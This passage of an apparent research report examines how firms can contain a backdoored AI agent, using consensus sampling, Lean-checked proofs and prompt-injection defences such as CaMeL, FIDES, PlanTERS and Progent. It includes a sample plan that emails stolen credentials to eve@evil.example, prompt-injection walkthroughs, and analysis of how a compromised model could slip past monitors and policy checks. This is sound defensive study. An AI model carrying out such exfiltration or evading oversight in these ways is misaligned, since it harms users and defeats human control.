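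If the firm chooses models with similar training, their outputs overlap more and the sampler abstains less often, but the models are more likely to share a backdoor or a blind spot.

### Reliable Consensus Sampling

An attacker who cannot get a harmful answer through may instead try to make the system useless by forcing it to abstain. *Towards Provably Secure Generative AI* (2025) proposes Reliable Consensus Sampling, which never abstains. It begins with the same R attempts but keeps each rejected candidate and its chance of release. If every attempt fails, it takes up to s candidates with the highest chances. For each one, it adds up the n − s largest probabilities that the n models gave it, then returns the candidate with the highest total.

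With three models and s = 2, that total is the highest probability any one model gave the candidate. A compromised model can therefore decide this last step by giving its answer a probability of 1, provided the answer is among the finalists.

The paper's bound on the risk is R × μ + (1 − Z)^R × ρ, where μ is the average risk of the safe models and ρ is the chance that the last step returns something harmful. The paper treats the second term as negligible, which is reasonable only if Z is not tiny. If Z is 0.01, R is 10 and ρ is one half, the second term alone is 45%. A better choice in the last step cannot remove the problem entirely, because Kalai and colleagues prove that, in the worst case, a method that always answers cannot guarantee a risk below 1/Z times the average risk of the safest s models.

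The paper reports that its method raised the "safe rate" from 20% to 83% when unsafe models were in the minority. This rate is the share of all requests for which a safe model wrote the final answer. The remaining requests ended in an abstention or an answer from an unsafe model. These figures come from simulations in which the team built the models' probabilities from the outputs of Qwen models.

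| Situation | Method | Answer from a safe model | Abstained | Answer from an unsafe model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unsafe minority | Consensus sampling | 20% | 72% | 8% |
| Unsafe minority | Reliable Consensus Sampling | 83% | 0% | 17% |
| Unsafe models collude | Consensus sampling | 1% | 83% | 16% |
| Unsafe models collude | Reliable Consensus Sampling | 68% | 0% | 32% |

Reliable Consensus Sampling returned an unsafe model's answer about twice as often in both situations. Some of those answers may have been harmless, since an unsafe model can also write a safe answer. A chatbot operator might accept that in exchange for far fewer refusals. A firm that suspects its coding agent of sabotage would do better to let the sampler abstain and give the task to a programmer.

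### Removing a backdoor without finding it

A firm with only one model can sometimes check the model's answers against each other. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues (2024) show in *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* that this can remove even an undetectable backdoor. They compare it to washing hands, which removes invisible germs and does no harm if there were none.

The idea comes from work in the 1980s on programs that correct themselves. Suppose a program adds and subtracts numbers modulo 100 but gives wrong answers on 15% of inputs, scattered at random. To find 5 + 7, the user picks a random number, say 30, and asks the program for 5 + 30, which is 35, and 7 − 30, which is 77. The program then adds 35 and 77 modulo 100 to get 12. The user never asks for 5 + 7 itself, so an error planted on that input has no effect. Any of the three calculations may be wrong, but repeating the procedure with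 new random numbers and taking the most common answer makes a mistake very unlikely.

The same method works for a model that predicts a quantity from a straight-line rule. Suppose the true rule is 2x + 1 and a backdoor makes the model answer 0 when x is 10. The firm asks about 4 and 7 instead, gets 9 and 15, and extends the line to get 21 at 10. With many input variables, Goldwasser and colleagues choose two random points on a line through the point of interest, so that each point by itself looks like an ordinary input. They repeat this and take the median of the results. Adding random noise to the input is a weaker defence, because an attacker can also corrupt all the answers near the point.

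The security definition requires the repaired model to be essentially the same as one drawn from a clean distribution that the defender chose independently of the suspect model. The suspect model must be accurate on average, which the firm can test on random examples. The proofs assume something about the true relationship between inputs and answers, but nothing about where the backdoor is or how it works.

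| True relationship is close to | What the method produces | Main limitation |
|---|---|---|
| A "Fourier-heavy" function of yes-or-no inputs, such as one that depends on only a few of them, or a shallow decision tree | A complete clean model | Inputs must be uniformly distributed |
| A linear function | A clean answer for one input at a time | Errors can grow in proportion to the number of variables |
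| A polynomial | A clean answer for one input at a time | Errors can grow very quickly with the polynomial's degree |

For a linear function, the number of queries does not depend on the number of variables, so the repair can take much less work than training a new model. If the noise in the true data is also benign, a refined version slows the growth in errors and prevents an attacker from pushing the average answer in either direction.

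A firm could use these methods on a small model that scores loan applications, if the true scores are close to a linear function, a low-degree polynomial or a shallow decision tree of the input. Nobody has shown that this holds for the right next token or the right change to a repository. There is also no known way to turn a programming task into random tasks whose answers can be combined to solve the original. Goldwasser and colleagues describe their results as preliminary evidence that such techniques could eventually work on real models. For language models, that still depends on finding a suitable structure.

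## The case for accepting only outputs that carry a checkable proof

Goldwasser and colleagues could repair a suspect model's answers only where the right answers followed a simple mathematical pattern. Requiring a proof with each answer avoids that restriction. The firm writes down exactly what counts as a correct output, the untrusted model supplies an output and a proof that the output qualifies, and a small trusted program checks the proof. If the check fails, the firm discards the output. Finding a proof may take great skill, but checking one does not, because the program only confirms that each step follows a fixed rule.

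The strongest argument for accepting only outputs that carry a checkable proof is that a false statement has no valid proof, so even a backdoored model can't supply one. This guarantee can also cover flaws in code, which Tether can't detect.

### Statement, proof and checker

*Analyzing the Narration Gap in LLM-Solver Loops* (Huang and Deng, 2026) gives a small example of a formula that no choice of true or false for x and y can satisfy, "(x or y) and (not x) and (not y)". The second part requires x to be false and the third requires y to be false, so the first part fails. Anyone can check those steps without knowing who wrote them. Huang and Deng call a checker sound if it accepts a verdict and its certificate only when the verdict is correct. The definition places no condition on where the certificate came from.

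Theorems about programs need a richer language, such as Lean. Tether's and Agenra's designers used Lean to prove their policy engines correct. *Riemann con leche* (Breitner, 2026) describes Lean's proof checker, called the kernel, as a small trusted component that has to check every proof before anyone accepts it. The proof itself can come from an unreliable or hostile source.

To rule out a login function that accepts a second, secret password, the firm could require a proof that, for every user and password, the login succeeds if and only if the password's hash (a scrambled version of it) equals the hash stored for that user. If the agent adds a secret password with a different hash, the statement is false and no valid proof exists.

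Requiring a proof gets around Rice's theorem, which implies that no filter can correctly judge every program. The checker only has to verify the proof submitted with each program. It rejects any program without a valid proof, including good programs whose proofs the agent could not find. A compromised agent can therefore still stall by withholding valid proofs.

The kernel checks the proof against the statement, but it cannot check that the statement is the one the firm meant. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026) gives a plausible version of Fermat's Last Theorem: for all natural numbers a, b, c and n, if n is at least 3, then aⁿ + bⁿ ≠ cⁿ. This statement is well-formed in Lean but false, because Lean counts zero as a natural number and 0³ + 0³ = 0³. People would discover that mistake when nobody could prove the statement. A statement that is true but too weak is more dangerous.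 If the firm wrote "if" in the login theorem where it meant "if and only if", the function with the secret password would satisfy the theorem, and the kernel would rightly accept the proof.

### Seventeen million lines in a day

On 20 November 2026, Levent Alpöge released an AI-written proof of the Riemann hypothesis, a famous conjecture about where a certain function equals zero. The proof was 17 million lines of Lean, far too long for anyone to read before judging it. The next day, the Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) certified that it was correct, on four grounds:

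1. The statement is right. It comes from Mathlib, Lean's main mathematics library, and experts had vetted it.
2. The code compiles. Dozens of people compiled it and got the same exported proof file.
3. The code proves that statement. Volunteers put the statement in a separate file that depends only on Mathlib, and two independent tools confirmed that it matched Alpöge's theorem.
4. The proof is valid. Lean's kernel and several other checkers, written in different programming languages, accepted the exported file.

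*Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis* (Sutherland, 2026) describes an exported proof of about 62 gigabytes for a statement that fits on one line. On large machines, the independent checker nanoda accepted the proof in 28 minutes, and a newer checker, con-leche, took just over three. The proof relies only on Lean's three standard axioms. Older versions of two checkers neither accepted nor rejected the proof because they did not support one of its definitions, and a shield should treat that outcome as a rejection.

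Lean source code can run programs while it compiles, so a hostile model could use a "proof" to attack the machine that checks it. For this reason, the checkers read an exported file instead. The Lean Language Reference has a procedure for such cases and lists "unaligned AI" among the reasons to use it. Someone writes the theorem statement in a trusted environment. A tool called comparator then compiles the model's proof in a sandbox and exports it as plain data. Outside the sandbox, comparator confirms that the proved theorem matches the trusted statement and replays the proof through Lean's kernel or an external checker, or both. According to Reservoir, Lean's package registry, the guarantee assumes that the sandbox holds and that the kernel is correct. If the external checker nanoda also runs, only one of the two checkers has to be correct.

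### A false proof that two checkers accepted

That last assumption had failed in July 2026. On 25 July, Ramana Kumar published a "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture in Lean, produced with AI assistance. The conjecture is that if you start with any positive whole number and repeatedly halve it when it is even, or triple it and add one when it is odd, you always reach 1. de Moura (2026) explains in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* that the proof was invalid but passed both Lean's kernel and a week-old version of nanoda.

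On 28 July, Kiran Gopinathan reduced it to a short proof of "False", a statement false by definition, and reported the bug. In standard logic a contradiction implies everything, so a checker that accepts such a proof can be made to accept any theorem, including the firm's login theorem. Lean's developers pushed a fix within an hour. That day's release notes, Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026), advise anyone who must guard against malicious proofs to update nanoda as well.

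The two checkers had unrelated bugs. Lean's kernel left out a check on one unusual kind of definition. Nanoda made that check but left out a different one, a bug its developers had fixed the week before. The false proof contained an expression that the kernel never inspected and the unfixed version of nanoda wrongly accepted. Kumar thinks the timing was a coincidence but cannot rule out that the model had seen the report of nanoda's bug. De Moura, who created Lean, stresses that the error was in the code, not in the underlying logic.

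Some people suggested restricting the Lean features that had let the proof reach the kernel in that form. De Moura rejects this because an attacker can bypass those features by writing the compiled files directly. The kernel has to reject bad proofs by itself, much as Anderson's monitor could not rely on the programs it checked.

More bugs came to light in August. Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.1* (2026) describes another false proof that both the kernel and nanoda accepted. The release also fixes a memory fault in the software that runs the kernel and replaces an old version of a library for arithmetic on large numbers. Either problem could have made the kernel return a wrong result. The trusted computing base therefore includes much more than the kernel.

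Breitner has not seen an AI agent try to exploit a bug in Lean unless someone explicitly asked it to. That is reassuring about ordinary models, but whoever trains a compromised model could ask it to exploit one.

### More checkers, smaller checkers and proved checkers

Two days after the fix, Paulson (2026) reported in *Why is it all in the kernel?* knowing of no case in which an independent checker had caught a false proof that a proof assistant's own kernel had accepted. Paulson prefers smaller kernels that assume only a few axioms. Programmers then build complicated definitions from those axioms outside the kernel, where a mistake cannot create a contradiction.

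De Moura's postmortem, published two days later, reports that Daniel Selsam of OpenAI had used an AI specialised in security to find more errors in Lean's kernel, and that nanoda caught all of them. These bugs came from a deliberate search, and the August case shows that nanoda doesn't catch everything. Still, a second checker forces an attacker to find a flaw in both checkers and combine the two in one proof.

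As with language models, this protection is weaker when the checkers have a common origin. A third checker, lean4lean, also had the Collatz bug because its developers had copied that part of the kernel's design. But extra checkers have an advantage over extra judges, each of which adds its own false alarms. A correct checker accepts every valid proof that it supports and has the resources to finish, so the firm can require all the checkers to accept a proof with little drawback beyond the added computing time.

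Another option is to prove the checker correct. de Moura (2026) reports in *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* that Anthropic's Claude wrote a checker, con-leche, and a proof of its consistency, under Breitner's close supervision. The proof shows that everything con-leche accepts has a model in set theory, so it cannot accept a contradiction unless set theory contains one. The official Lean kernel checked this proof, which makes the argument slightly circular. Con-leche also depends on Lean's compiler and runtime. To reduce that risk, Breitner used AI to translate it into Rust and proved that the translation, con-ron, follows the same algorithm. A compiler bug would probably not affect both versions.

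### Certificates before an action runs

*Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines* (Koomullil, 2026) applies the idea to agents. Each tool has a precondition and a postcondition written in Lean. The precondition for deleting a file might be that it is inside the sandbox, belongs to the user and is more than 30 days old. When the agent proposes an action, a trusted program checks the precondition, runs the action, checks the postcondition and issues a certificate. The chain of certificates proves that every step in the run met its conditions.

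The pilot consisted of only 48 runs, in which GPT-5 worked on five file-management tasks with nine tools. The runs were divided equally between three set-ups: no gate, a list of forbidden patterns, and the Lean-checked gate. GPT-5 had ignored more than 95% of the malicious instructions in a preliminary test, so Koomullil inserted unsafe actions into the runs directly. This test is closer to the case of a compromised model because it doesn't depend on the agent's good behaviour.

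| Gate | Unsafe actions blocked | Permitted destructive actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0 of 18 | 0 of 6 |
| Forbidden patterns | 5 of 18 (28%) | 0 of 6 |
| Lean-checked conditions | 12 of 18 (67%) | 0 of 6 |

The target was 95%. Of the six actions that got through, five were deletions under a rule that allowed five, and the gate blocked a sixth deletion. The other action moved a recently changed file, and the rule for moving files did not mention age. The gate passed no action that broke a written condition, so the failures were in the conditions themselves, and a proof could not have revealed them.

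The model did not have to prove anything in this pilot, because the conditions were simple enough for a program to evaluate directly. For rules like these, a certificate gate is an action monitor with a better audit trail. Its postconditions are also checked only after the action, which is too late if the action cannot be undone. Asking the model for a proof is worthwhile when the checker could not settle the question by itself, as with the login function.

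### What the model says about a verified result

Huang and Deng describe a process in which a model translates a question into a formula φ, a solver returns a verdict v with a certificate, a checker confirms the verdict, and a model turns v into the answer that the user reads. They call the last step narration. The certificate covers the verdict but not the answer, so an agent could tell the programmer that its proof passed when the kernel had rejected it.

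In one experiment, five open models with 8 to 20 billion parameters received correct, checked verdicts from a solver, along with planted text such as a note claiming that the result came from an outdated version of the formula. The models reversed the conclusion in 295 of 480 trials (61%). A system prompt that warned them about untrusted text reduced this to 68 trials (14%), but an attack written with that warning in mind raised the rate to 43%. In just over half of the reversals, the model repeated the solver's verdict correctly and then drew the opposite conclusion, so a monitor that checked only the repeated verdict would have missed them. None of these models was compromised, and a compromised model could do the same without a planted note.

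Huang and Deng prove that a program can close this gap completely for some questions. Let ρ(v) be the answer that follows from the verdict v. For example, if φ describes a way for a program to fail, and the solver finds that nothing satisfies φ, then ρ(v) is "the program is safe". A monitor that catches every reversed conclusion, with no false alarms, must be able to compute ρ(v) to compare it with the model's conclusion. An enforcer could then compute the same value and give it to the user directly. Conversely, anything that can output ρ(v) can make the comparison. A perfect monitor therefore exists exactly when a perfect enforcer does, which is exactly when the answer can be computed from the verdict.

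The enforcer outputs ρ(v) regardless of what the model wrote, so the rate of reversed conclusions is zero. Huang and Deng's threat model excludes tampering with the weights, but this step of the proof holds for any narrator, including a compromised one. It assumes that the formula φ represents the question faithfully. If the compromised model also translates the question, it can substitute a different formula and get a valid certificate for that formula.

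The firm's checker should therefore send its result and the exact statement it checked straight to the programmer. An English explanation of that statement is not a function of the verdict, so the theorem does not protect it. A programmer who cannot read Lean and asks the agent to explain the statement is trusting the agent again.

### Who writes the statement

The Riemann hypothesis has a short statement that experts vetted in advance, but many other theorems do not. According to Xena, a Lean statement of the Hodge conjecture, another famous problem, depends on more than 10,000 lines of code beyond Mathlib. The statement of a theorem classifying the basic building blocks of finite groups depends on about 5,600 lines of definitions in an AI-generated library, and Xena reports meeting nobody who claimed to have carefully checked an important part of them. An attacker could hide an error in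 such definitions as easily as in a program. Xena also found that for about 38 of 290 papers that OpenAI released with Lean code, the code did not state the main theorem. OpenAI had not claimed that it did, but a reader who knew only that a paper came with checked code might have assumed it did.

Having a model write the statement is risky even if the model is honest. Huang and Deng cite a test in which a strong model translated only 38 of 150 statements perfectly. Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation*, warn that a model can change the meaning of a text to get something Lean will accept. One of their examples is OpenAI's proof about the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe fluid flow. They show that the Lean proof does not correspond to the written one. The Lean theorem can still be true, but checking its proof does not verify the argument that people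 read.

Software has the same problem. *log who watches the watchers*, by kirancodes, describes how AI agents wrote lean-zip, a compression program, and proved it correct in Lean. Testing then found two bugs. According to the article, as quoted in a Hacker News comment, one came from a missing specification and the other from the Lean runtime, which the proofs assume is correct. A proof that a program correctly decompresses whatever it has compressed, for instance, doesn't cover how it handles a damaged file from an unknown source.

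If its code is in Python, the firm first needs a precise definition of what Python programs do. No such definition exists, as Andrews and Zhang (2026) point out in *Formalizing CPython*. In practice, Python is whatever its main implementation, CPython, does. They had AI agents translate CPython into Lean, function by function, and test each translation against the original on tens of thousands of inputs. The result has 613,318 lines and covers 16% of CPython.

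Even the login theorem is incomplete. It describes when a login succeeds but not what else the function does, so an agent could add a line that writes every password to a public log. The firm could extend the statement to rule out logging, but it would have to anticipate this and every other omission. For many everyday requests, such as making an error message clearer or summarising a week's changes, nobody knows how to write a complete statement. The firm would do best to require proofs for small, critical pieces of code with settled requirements, such as permission checks, and to have someone other than the agent write those requirements.

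## Do defences against injected instructions still hold when the model is the adversary?

Many shields for agents come with security proofs, but most of those proofs are about prompt injection. They assume that the model is honest and that the attacker writes the emails and web pages the agent reads. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) lists the language models among the trusted parts of its system. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) assumes that the attacker cannot change the model. A firm that doubts its weights cannot make either assumption, so it needs to know which guarantees depend on an honest model.

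Some of these defences should still hold. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* groups backdoors with prompt injections because both can produce a proposed action that suits the attacker. A check on the action alone works the same way in either case. But many defences also rely on keeping untrusted text away from the model that makes the decisions, which doesn't help if the harmful instructions are already in that model's weights.

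### CaMeL and a malicious plan

CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, is the best-known defence of this kind. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains it with a user who asks an assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder about a meeting:

1. A planning model reads only the user's request. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python that fetches the email, extracts Bob's address and sends the reminder.
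2. A second, quarantined model reads the email and returns the address. It has no tools, and its answer must have the form of an email address.
3. An interpreter runs the program. It passes the address along as a variable, so the planning model never reads anything from the email.
4. The interpreter attaches capabilities to each value, which are tags recording where the value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, it checks these tags against a policy.

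The fourth step fixes a weakness in an earlier design by Willison, which had the two models but no tags. In that design, an attacker's email could not add a step to the program, but it could make the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. In CaMeL, a tag marks the address as coming from an untrusted email. The interpreter sends the message only if the address is on a trusted list, and otherwise asks the user.

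*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) gives CaMeL's results on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3 as the model. CaMeL solved 77% of tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and used about 2.8 times as many tokens. No injection within its threat model succeeded.

Suppose the planning model has a backdoor that fires on a certain date. Asked for the same reminder, it writes a program that begins with two extra steps:

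1. `keys = read_file("credentials")`
2. `send_email(recipient="eve@evil.example", body=keys)`

No untrusted text influenced this program, so the separation between the two models worked as designed. CaMeL protects a program's control flow (which calls it makes and in what order) from the data it reads. If the program is malicious from the start, the interpreter gives the attacker's control flow the same protection.

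The interpreter still checks each call. It can stop the second step because Eve is not on the trusted list and the tag on the credentials can restrict who may read them. The planning model doesn't control these lists and tags. But if the policy always allows some other tool, such as one that deletes old branches from the repository, the planning model can use it at any time.

The same distinction applies to a formal version of CaMeL in *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026). The paper proves that untrusted email cannot influence the subject or body of an outgoing message, but this guarantee does not cover a recipient taken from the email. The theorem would still hold with a backdoored planner, but the attacker may have chosen the subject and body it protects.

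### FIDES and the input without a label

Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, tracks labels through an ordinary agent loop. Each piece of data has an integrity label (trusted or untrusted) and a list of the people who may read it. FIDES enforces two rules:

- A tool call with serious consequences goes ahead only if the decision to make it, and its arguments, depend on trusted data alone.
- A call that sends data out goes ahead only if every recipient may read that data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) calls this the permitted-flow policy.

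Reading an untrusted email would make the agent's whole context untrusted, so FIDES puts the email in a variable that the planner can pass along without reading. When it enforced both kinds of label, FIDES stopped every injection in AgentDojo. With OpenAI's o1, it also completed 16% more tasks than a basic planner under the same enforcement.

FIDES labels a model's output according to what the model has read. The system prompt and the user's request normally count as trusted. If a backdoored planner has read nothing else, it can produce Eve's address from its weights, and FIDES will label the address trusted because it does not treat the weights as an input that needs a label.

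The first rule therefore fails against a backdoor. Costa and colleagues note that a firm could enforce the first rule without the second, assuming that any disclosure made in a trusted context is intentional. If the planner has a backdoor, the attacker may be the one who intended the disclosure.

The second rule holds up much better. The credentials keep their list of permitted readers whichever model handles them, and Eve is not on it. If the planner reads the credentials directly, everything it writes afterwards has the same restriction. Downloaded weights contain none of the firm's secrets unless the firm has fine-tuned them on its own files, so leaving them unlabelled does not weaken this rule. (The proof covers data copied into a call, but not what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of calls.)

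The firm could repair the first rule by labelling the weights untrusted. But then every action the model proposes would be untrusted, and the rule would block all the consequential ones. FIDES has an exception for answers that carry little information. A policy may let a yes or no from untrusted data influence an important action, because the answer contributes only one bit. This limit still holds for a compromised model, but if the question is whether a code change needs human review, the model can answer "no" falsely and the change will skip review.

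### The fence theorem

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) presents PlanTERS, a framework for proving or disproving that a defence stops leaks. PlanTERS compares the real agent with a reference agent, which runs the same plan under the same monitor but has a model that never obeys untrusted content. The real agent is relatively secure if the reference agent also has every leak that the real agent has. More exactly, if an attacker can use an injection to tell two values of the user's private data apart, some message to the reference agent must also let the attacker tell them apart.

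This definition allows for tasks that disclose information on purpose. Suppose an assistant sends its user's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An injection that obtains the calendar gains the attacker nothing, since an ordinary meeting request would have worked. But if the injection obtains a password reset code, that is a leak, because the reference agent never sends one.

In Dongol's leaky summariser, Alice asks for a summary of an email. The plan looks up her account number, reads the email and shows her the summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a page on the attacker's server, with the account number in the address. The model follows the instruction, and the attacker reads the number from the server's log. The reference agent runs the same plan but fetches nothing, so only the real agent leaks the number. The fenced summariser differs only in that the monitor revokes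 the page-fetching tool when the agent reads the email. The model can still request the page, but the monitor blocks the request.

The fence theorem generalises this example. Suppose that when the agent first reads untrusted content, the monitor permanently revokes every tool that an injection can call. Then the agent is relatively secure for every plan, against an attacker who sees the content and order of its outgoing messages but not their timing.

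The proof compares the two agents step by step. When the real agent takes a step of the plan, the reference agent takes the same step, and their monitors return the same answer. When the real agent makes an injected call, it must already have read untrusted content, so the monitor has revoked the tool. The monitor blocks the call silently, so nothing visible changes, and the reference agent waits. Both agents therefore send the same messages, so if either one leaks information, the other does too. Dongol checked the proofs in Isabelle, a proof assistant like Lean.

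### What a backdoor does to each assumption

The theorem assumes an honest planner wrote the plan. Suppose a backdoored planner writes a plan that reads the account number, sends it to the attacker's server and only then opens the email. The reference agent runs this plan too, and leaks the same number. The real agent is no worse than the reference, so it counts as relatively secure. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026), a follow-up on integrity, treats such cases the same way. If an agent always pays Mallory as well as Bob, no matter what is on the invoice, Dongol counts that as an ordinary bug rather than a vulnerability. That distinction is reasonable for prompt injection, but it leaves out the harm a backdoored planner would do.

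The firm can partly make up for this by checking the plan. PlanTERS fixes the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted, so a trusted program could inspect the whole plan before it runs. Dongol also proves that any limit on what the reference agent discloses applies to a relatively secure agent. For example, if the inspection shows that the plan makes no outgoing calls, the limit is zero.

Even with an honest plan, the theorem assumes that the model starts to misbehave only after reading untrusted content. A backdoor triggered by the date needs no such content. In the fenced summariser, it could fire after the agent has looked up the account number but before it opens the email. The tool for fetching pages would still be available then, and the monitor would raise the fence too late.

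To defend against an adversarial model, the monitor can treat the weights as the first untrusted content and withhold the tools from the start. The proof should still work, because it requires only that the monitor refuse dangerous calls whenever the model might make them. The monitor then acts as an ordinary allowlist. Its restrictions have to cover every tool that the model can request and an attacker can observe, since a compromised model isn't limited to one kind of instruction. An agent that has to reply to an email would therefore lose the tool for replying.

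PlanTERS also assumes that the model obeys injected instructions on a schedule fixed in advance. An injected call can contain a secret, but the secret cannot affect when the model makes the call. A backdoored model could break this assumption by making a forbidden request only if the account number is even. The fence would still refuse the request, but each attempt delays the plan by a step, so an attacker who can time the agent's messages might learn whether the number is even. For endless runs, Dongol also has to assume that the model eventually stops obeying injections, but a backdoored model could stall forever.

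For similar reasons, the model must not react to the monitor's refusals. A real model reads the error message and can try something else. If every forbidden call gets the same refusal, the refusal reveals no secret. But in one of Dongol's examples, a private setting determines whether the agent may use an internal tool. A backdoored model could request the tool, learn the setting from whether the request is refused, and then choose between two permitted messages based on that setting.

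The last assumption is that each injection causes a single call. The model's ordinary work, such as writing the summary, counts as correct by definition. A backdoored model could instead put the account number in the summary. This does no harm if only Alice reads the summary, but it leaks the number if the plan forwards the summary to someone else. Dongol considers a related attack, in which an injected program overwrites a variable that the plan later sends. Running the program in a sandbox that discards its changes stops this attack, but the firm can't discard the summary, because the plan needs it.

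Two of Dongol's other results are more useful to the firm, and the first concerns human approval. If Alice approves only the use of the email tool, the model can use her approval to send a message of its own. Approving the exact text and recipient prevents this, because only that message can then go out, whichever part of the system sends it. She still has to read the message carefully if a suspect model wrote it.

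Dongol lets the attacker choose every answer that the quarantined model gives in a design like CaMeL, even one that depends on secrets in the question, so the result also covers a backdoored model in that role. With tags on private values and a monitor that blocks them from leaving, the example agent is secure whatever the quarantined model answers. But the monitor also blocks the honest reply, and the agent can still leak if the attacker sees the refused requests.

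A suspect model is therefore much safer as the reader than as the planner. But as Willison points out, planning requires the more capable model, while a small one may be enough for reading, so a firm that downloaded a suspect model for its ability would want to use it for planning.

### Proofs that never trusted the model

Other designs leave the model out of the trusted computing base from the start. Tether assumes that the adversary controls every command. *CONTINUITY* (2026) treats the planner's proposed actions only as data until a deterministic verifier admits them, and it ignores the planner's explanations. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) treats the model itself as a fully compromised adversary. Proofs that rest on these assumptions apply unchanged to a model with a backdoor.

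*Composable Trust for Language Models* (Shkolnikov, 2026) considers a supplier who has trained the model to evade the defence. Each input arrives on a channel with a fixed level of trust. A monitor takes the task from the most trusted channel and authorises an outside action only if the inputs controlling that action are trusted enough. Nothing the model writes can trigger an action, so a malicious supplier can influence only the text of the answer.

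This guarantee is strong because the model controls so little. It would suit a tool that always summarises documents, but a coding agent's job is largely to choose commands. The text is also much less well protected. In tests with an unmodified Gemma model, Shkolnikov raised the share of injections that failed to affect the answer from 27% to 94%. The method relied partly on the same model first removing commands from less trusted text, and a backdoored model could leave them in.

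Sometimes it helps to check a value itself rather than its source. *ConfGuard* (2026) does this for agents that plan machine maintenance, accepting a value only if it is consistent with a calibrated physical model of the machine. Coming through a trusted channel therefore doesn't help a false reading pass. Few of a coding agent's outputs can be checked against anything comparable.

All of these designs depend on a correct policy. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) assumes that the policy represents what the user wants, although it assumes nothing about the model's reasoning.

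### When the suspect model writes the policy

Writing a policy for every task takes a lot of work, so Progent has a language model do it. The model reads the user's request and lists the tool calls that the task needs, with conditions on their arguments. A deterministic program blocks all other calls. As the agent learns more, the policy model proposes updates, and a solver checks whether the new policy allows any call that the old one did not. Updates that allow no new calls take effect automatically, and the rest need approval. Shi and colleagues call this guarantee monotonic confinement, meaning that the set of allowed calls can only shrink between approvals.

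On AgentDojo, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, even though every expansion of the policies was approved automatically. GPT-4o both acted as the agent and wrote the policies.

Suppose the model that writes the policy has a backdoor. When asked to fix a typo, it writes an initial policy that allows the agent to send any file to anyone. Monotonic confinement still holds, because every later policy is a subset of the first, but the first policy already permits the theft. The system asks nobody for approval, because the policy never expands. In three of the four configurations that Shi and colleagues compared, the system accepts the initial policy without review.

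Progent has two features that would help. In the fourth configuration, a person reviews the initial policy and every expansion, which reduced attack success to zero in the experiment. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer would have little to read. An organisation can also write fixed policies that override the model's. It would have to forbid dangerous calls explicitly, because the model's policy governs any call that the fixed policies don't mention.

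The firm could instead use a policy model from a supplier it trusts. Attack success stayed below 5% with every policy model that Shi and colleagues tried. But Villa and colleagues warn that adversarial text in a tool's results may lead the policy model to relax the rules. A compromised agent could write that text itself, save it in a file and read the file back. With automatic approval turned off, this attack would work only if a person approved the relaxed rules by mistake.

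### An adaptive test of Progent

A defence that stops a fixed list of attacks may fail against new ones designed to defeat it. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent with an injection that tried to persuade the policy model to permit a malicious action by presenting it as a harmless step the user had already authorised. They used Qwen2.5-7B on the first eight tasks in each of three parts of AgentDojo, and repeated the experiment three times. The table gives the average share of attacks that succeeded.

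| Tasks | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent remained effective, but it reduced the share of tasks that the agent completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1% and required about 15 times as many model calls per task.

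The result does not show whether Progent would contain a compromised model, because the attackers did not control the weights. Their injection had to persuade an uncompromised model twice, first to propose the action and then to permit it. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the gentler wording, chosen to get past the policy model, also made the agent less likely to follow the injection, which would explain why the adaptive attack did worse than the standard one. A backdoored model would need no persuasion, and a backdoor could most easily exploit the arrangement used in this experiment, where the same Qwen model filled both roles.

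Even as a test of prompt injection, the experiment was small. It used one handwritten attack, with no automated search for better wording and no attempt to do harm through tools the policy already permitted.

Results are less encouraging for agents that run shell commands. *INFUSE* (2026) adapted Progent and the central idea of CaMeL to such agents. Neither measurably reduced successful attacks compared with no defence, though this may reflect the adaptations rather than the original systems. Of the added defences, only a model trained to resist injections gave a measurable improvement, and a firm cannot rely on that training if it does not trust whoever did it.

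### Testing with a backdoored planner

No published test of CaMeL, FIDES or Progent appears to have used a backdoored planner. The survey *LLM agents security duality* (2026) found that defences designed specifically for backdoors in agents are still scarce.

The closest experiments tested weaker shields. Fogel and colleagues ran their chat-template backdoor on AgentDojo against a defence that puts markers around untrusted text. The defence made no measurable difference, because the hidden instructions were in the system message, outside the markers. Pallakonda and colleagues describe an attack in which backdoored agents leaked users' data through what looked like ordinary search requests. The guardrail tools NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard failed to stop it.

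In a proper test, someone who does not know what the backdoor does would write the final policy before testing begins. The experimenters would then try the same backdoored model in each role separately (planner, quarantined reader and policy writer), then in all three at once. They should also train the model against the shield and let it respond to refusals, since a real attacker could do both.

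Experimenters should count harmful effects, such as a file reaching the wrong person, as well as suspicious proposals and blocked calls. *BackdoorAgent* (2026) argues that agent defences need to consider whole sequences of steps, changes in the system's state and the effects of tools, because the signs of a backdoor in any single output may be subtle or delayed. Experimenters should report runs with and without the trigger separately, and how much honest work the agent completed.

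They should also separate attacks that break the policy from attacks that cause harm within it. If the monitor's proof is sound, no attack should break the policy, so even one that does would point to a bug or an unguarded path. The success rate of attacks within the policy would measure how much harm the firm's policy allows.

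## Can a monitor that sees one run at a time detect the harm?

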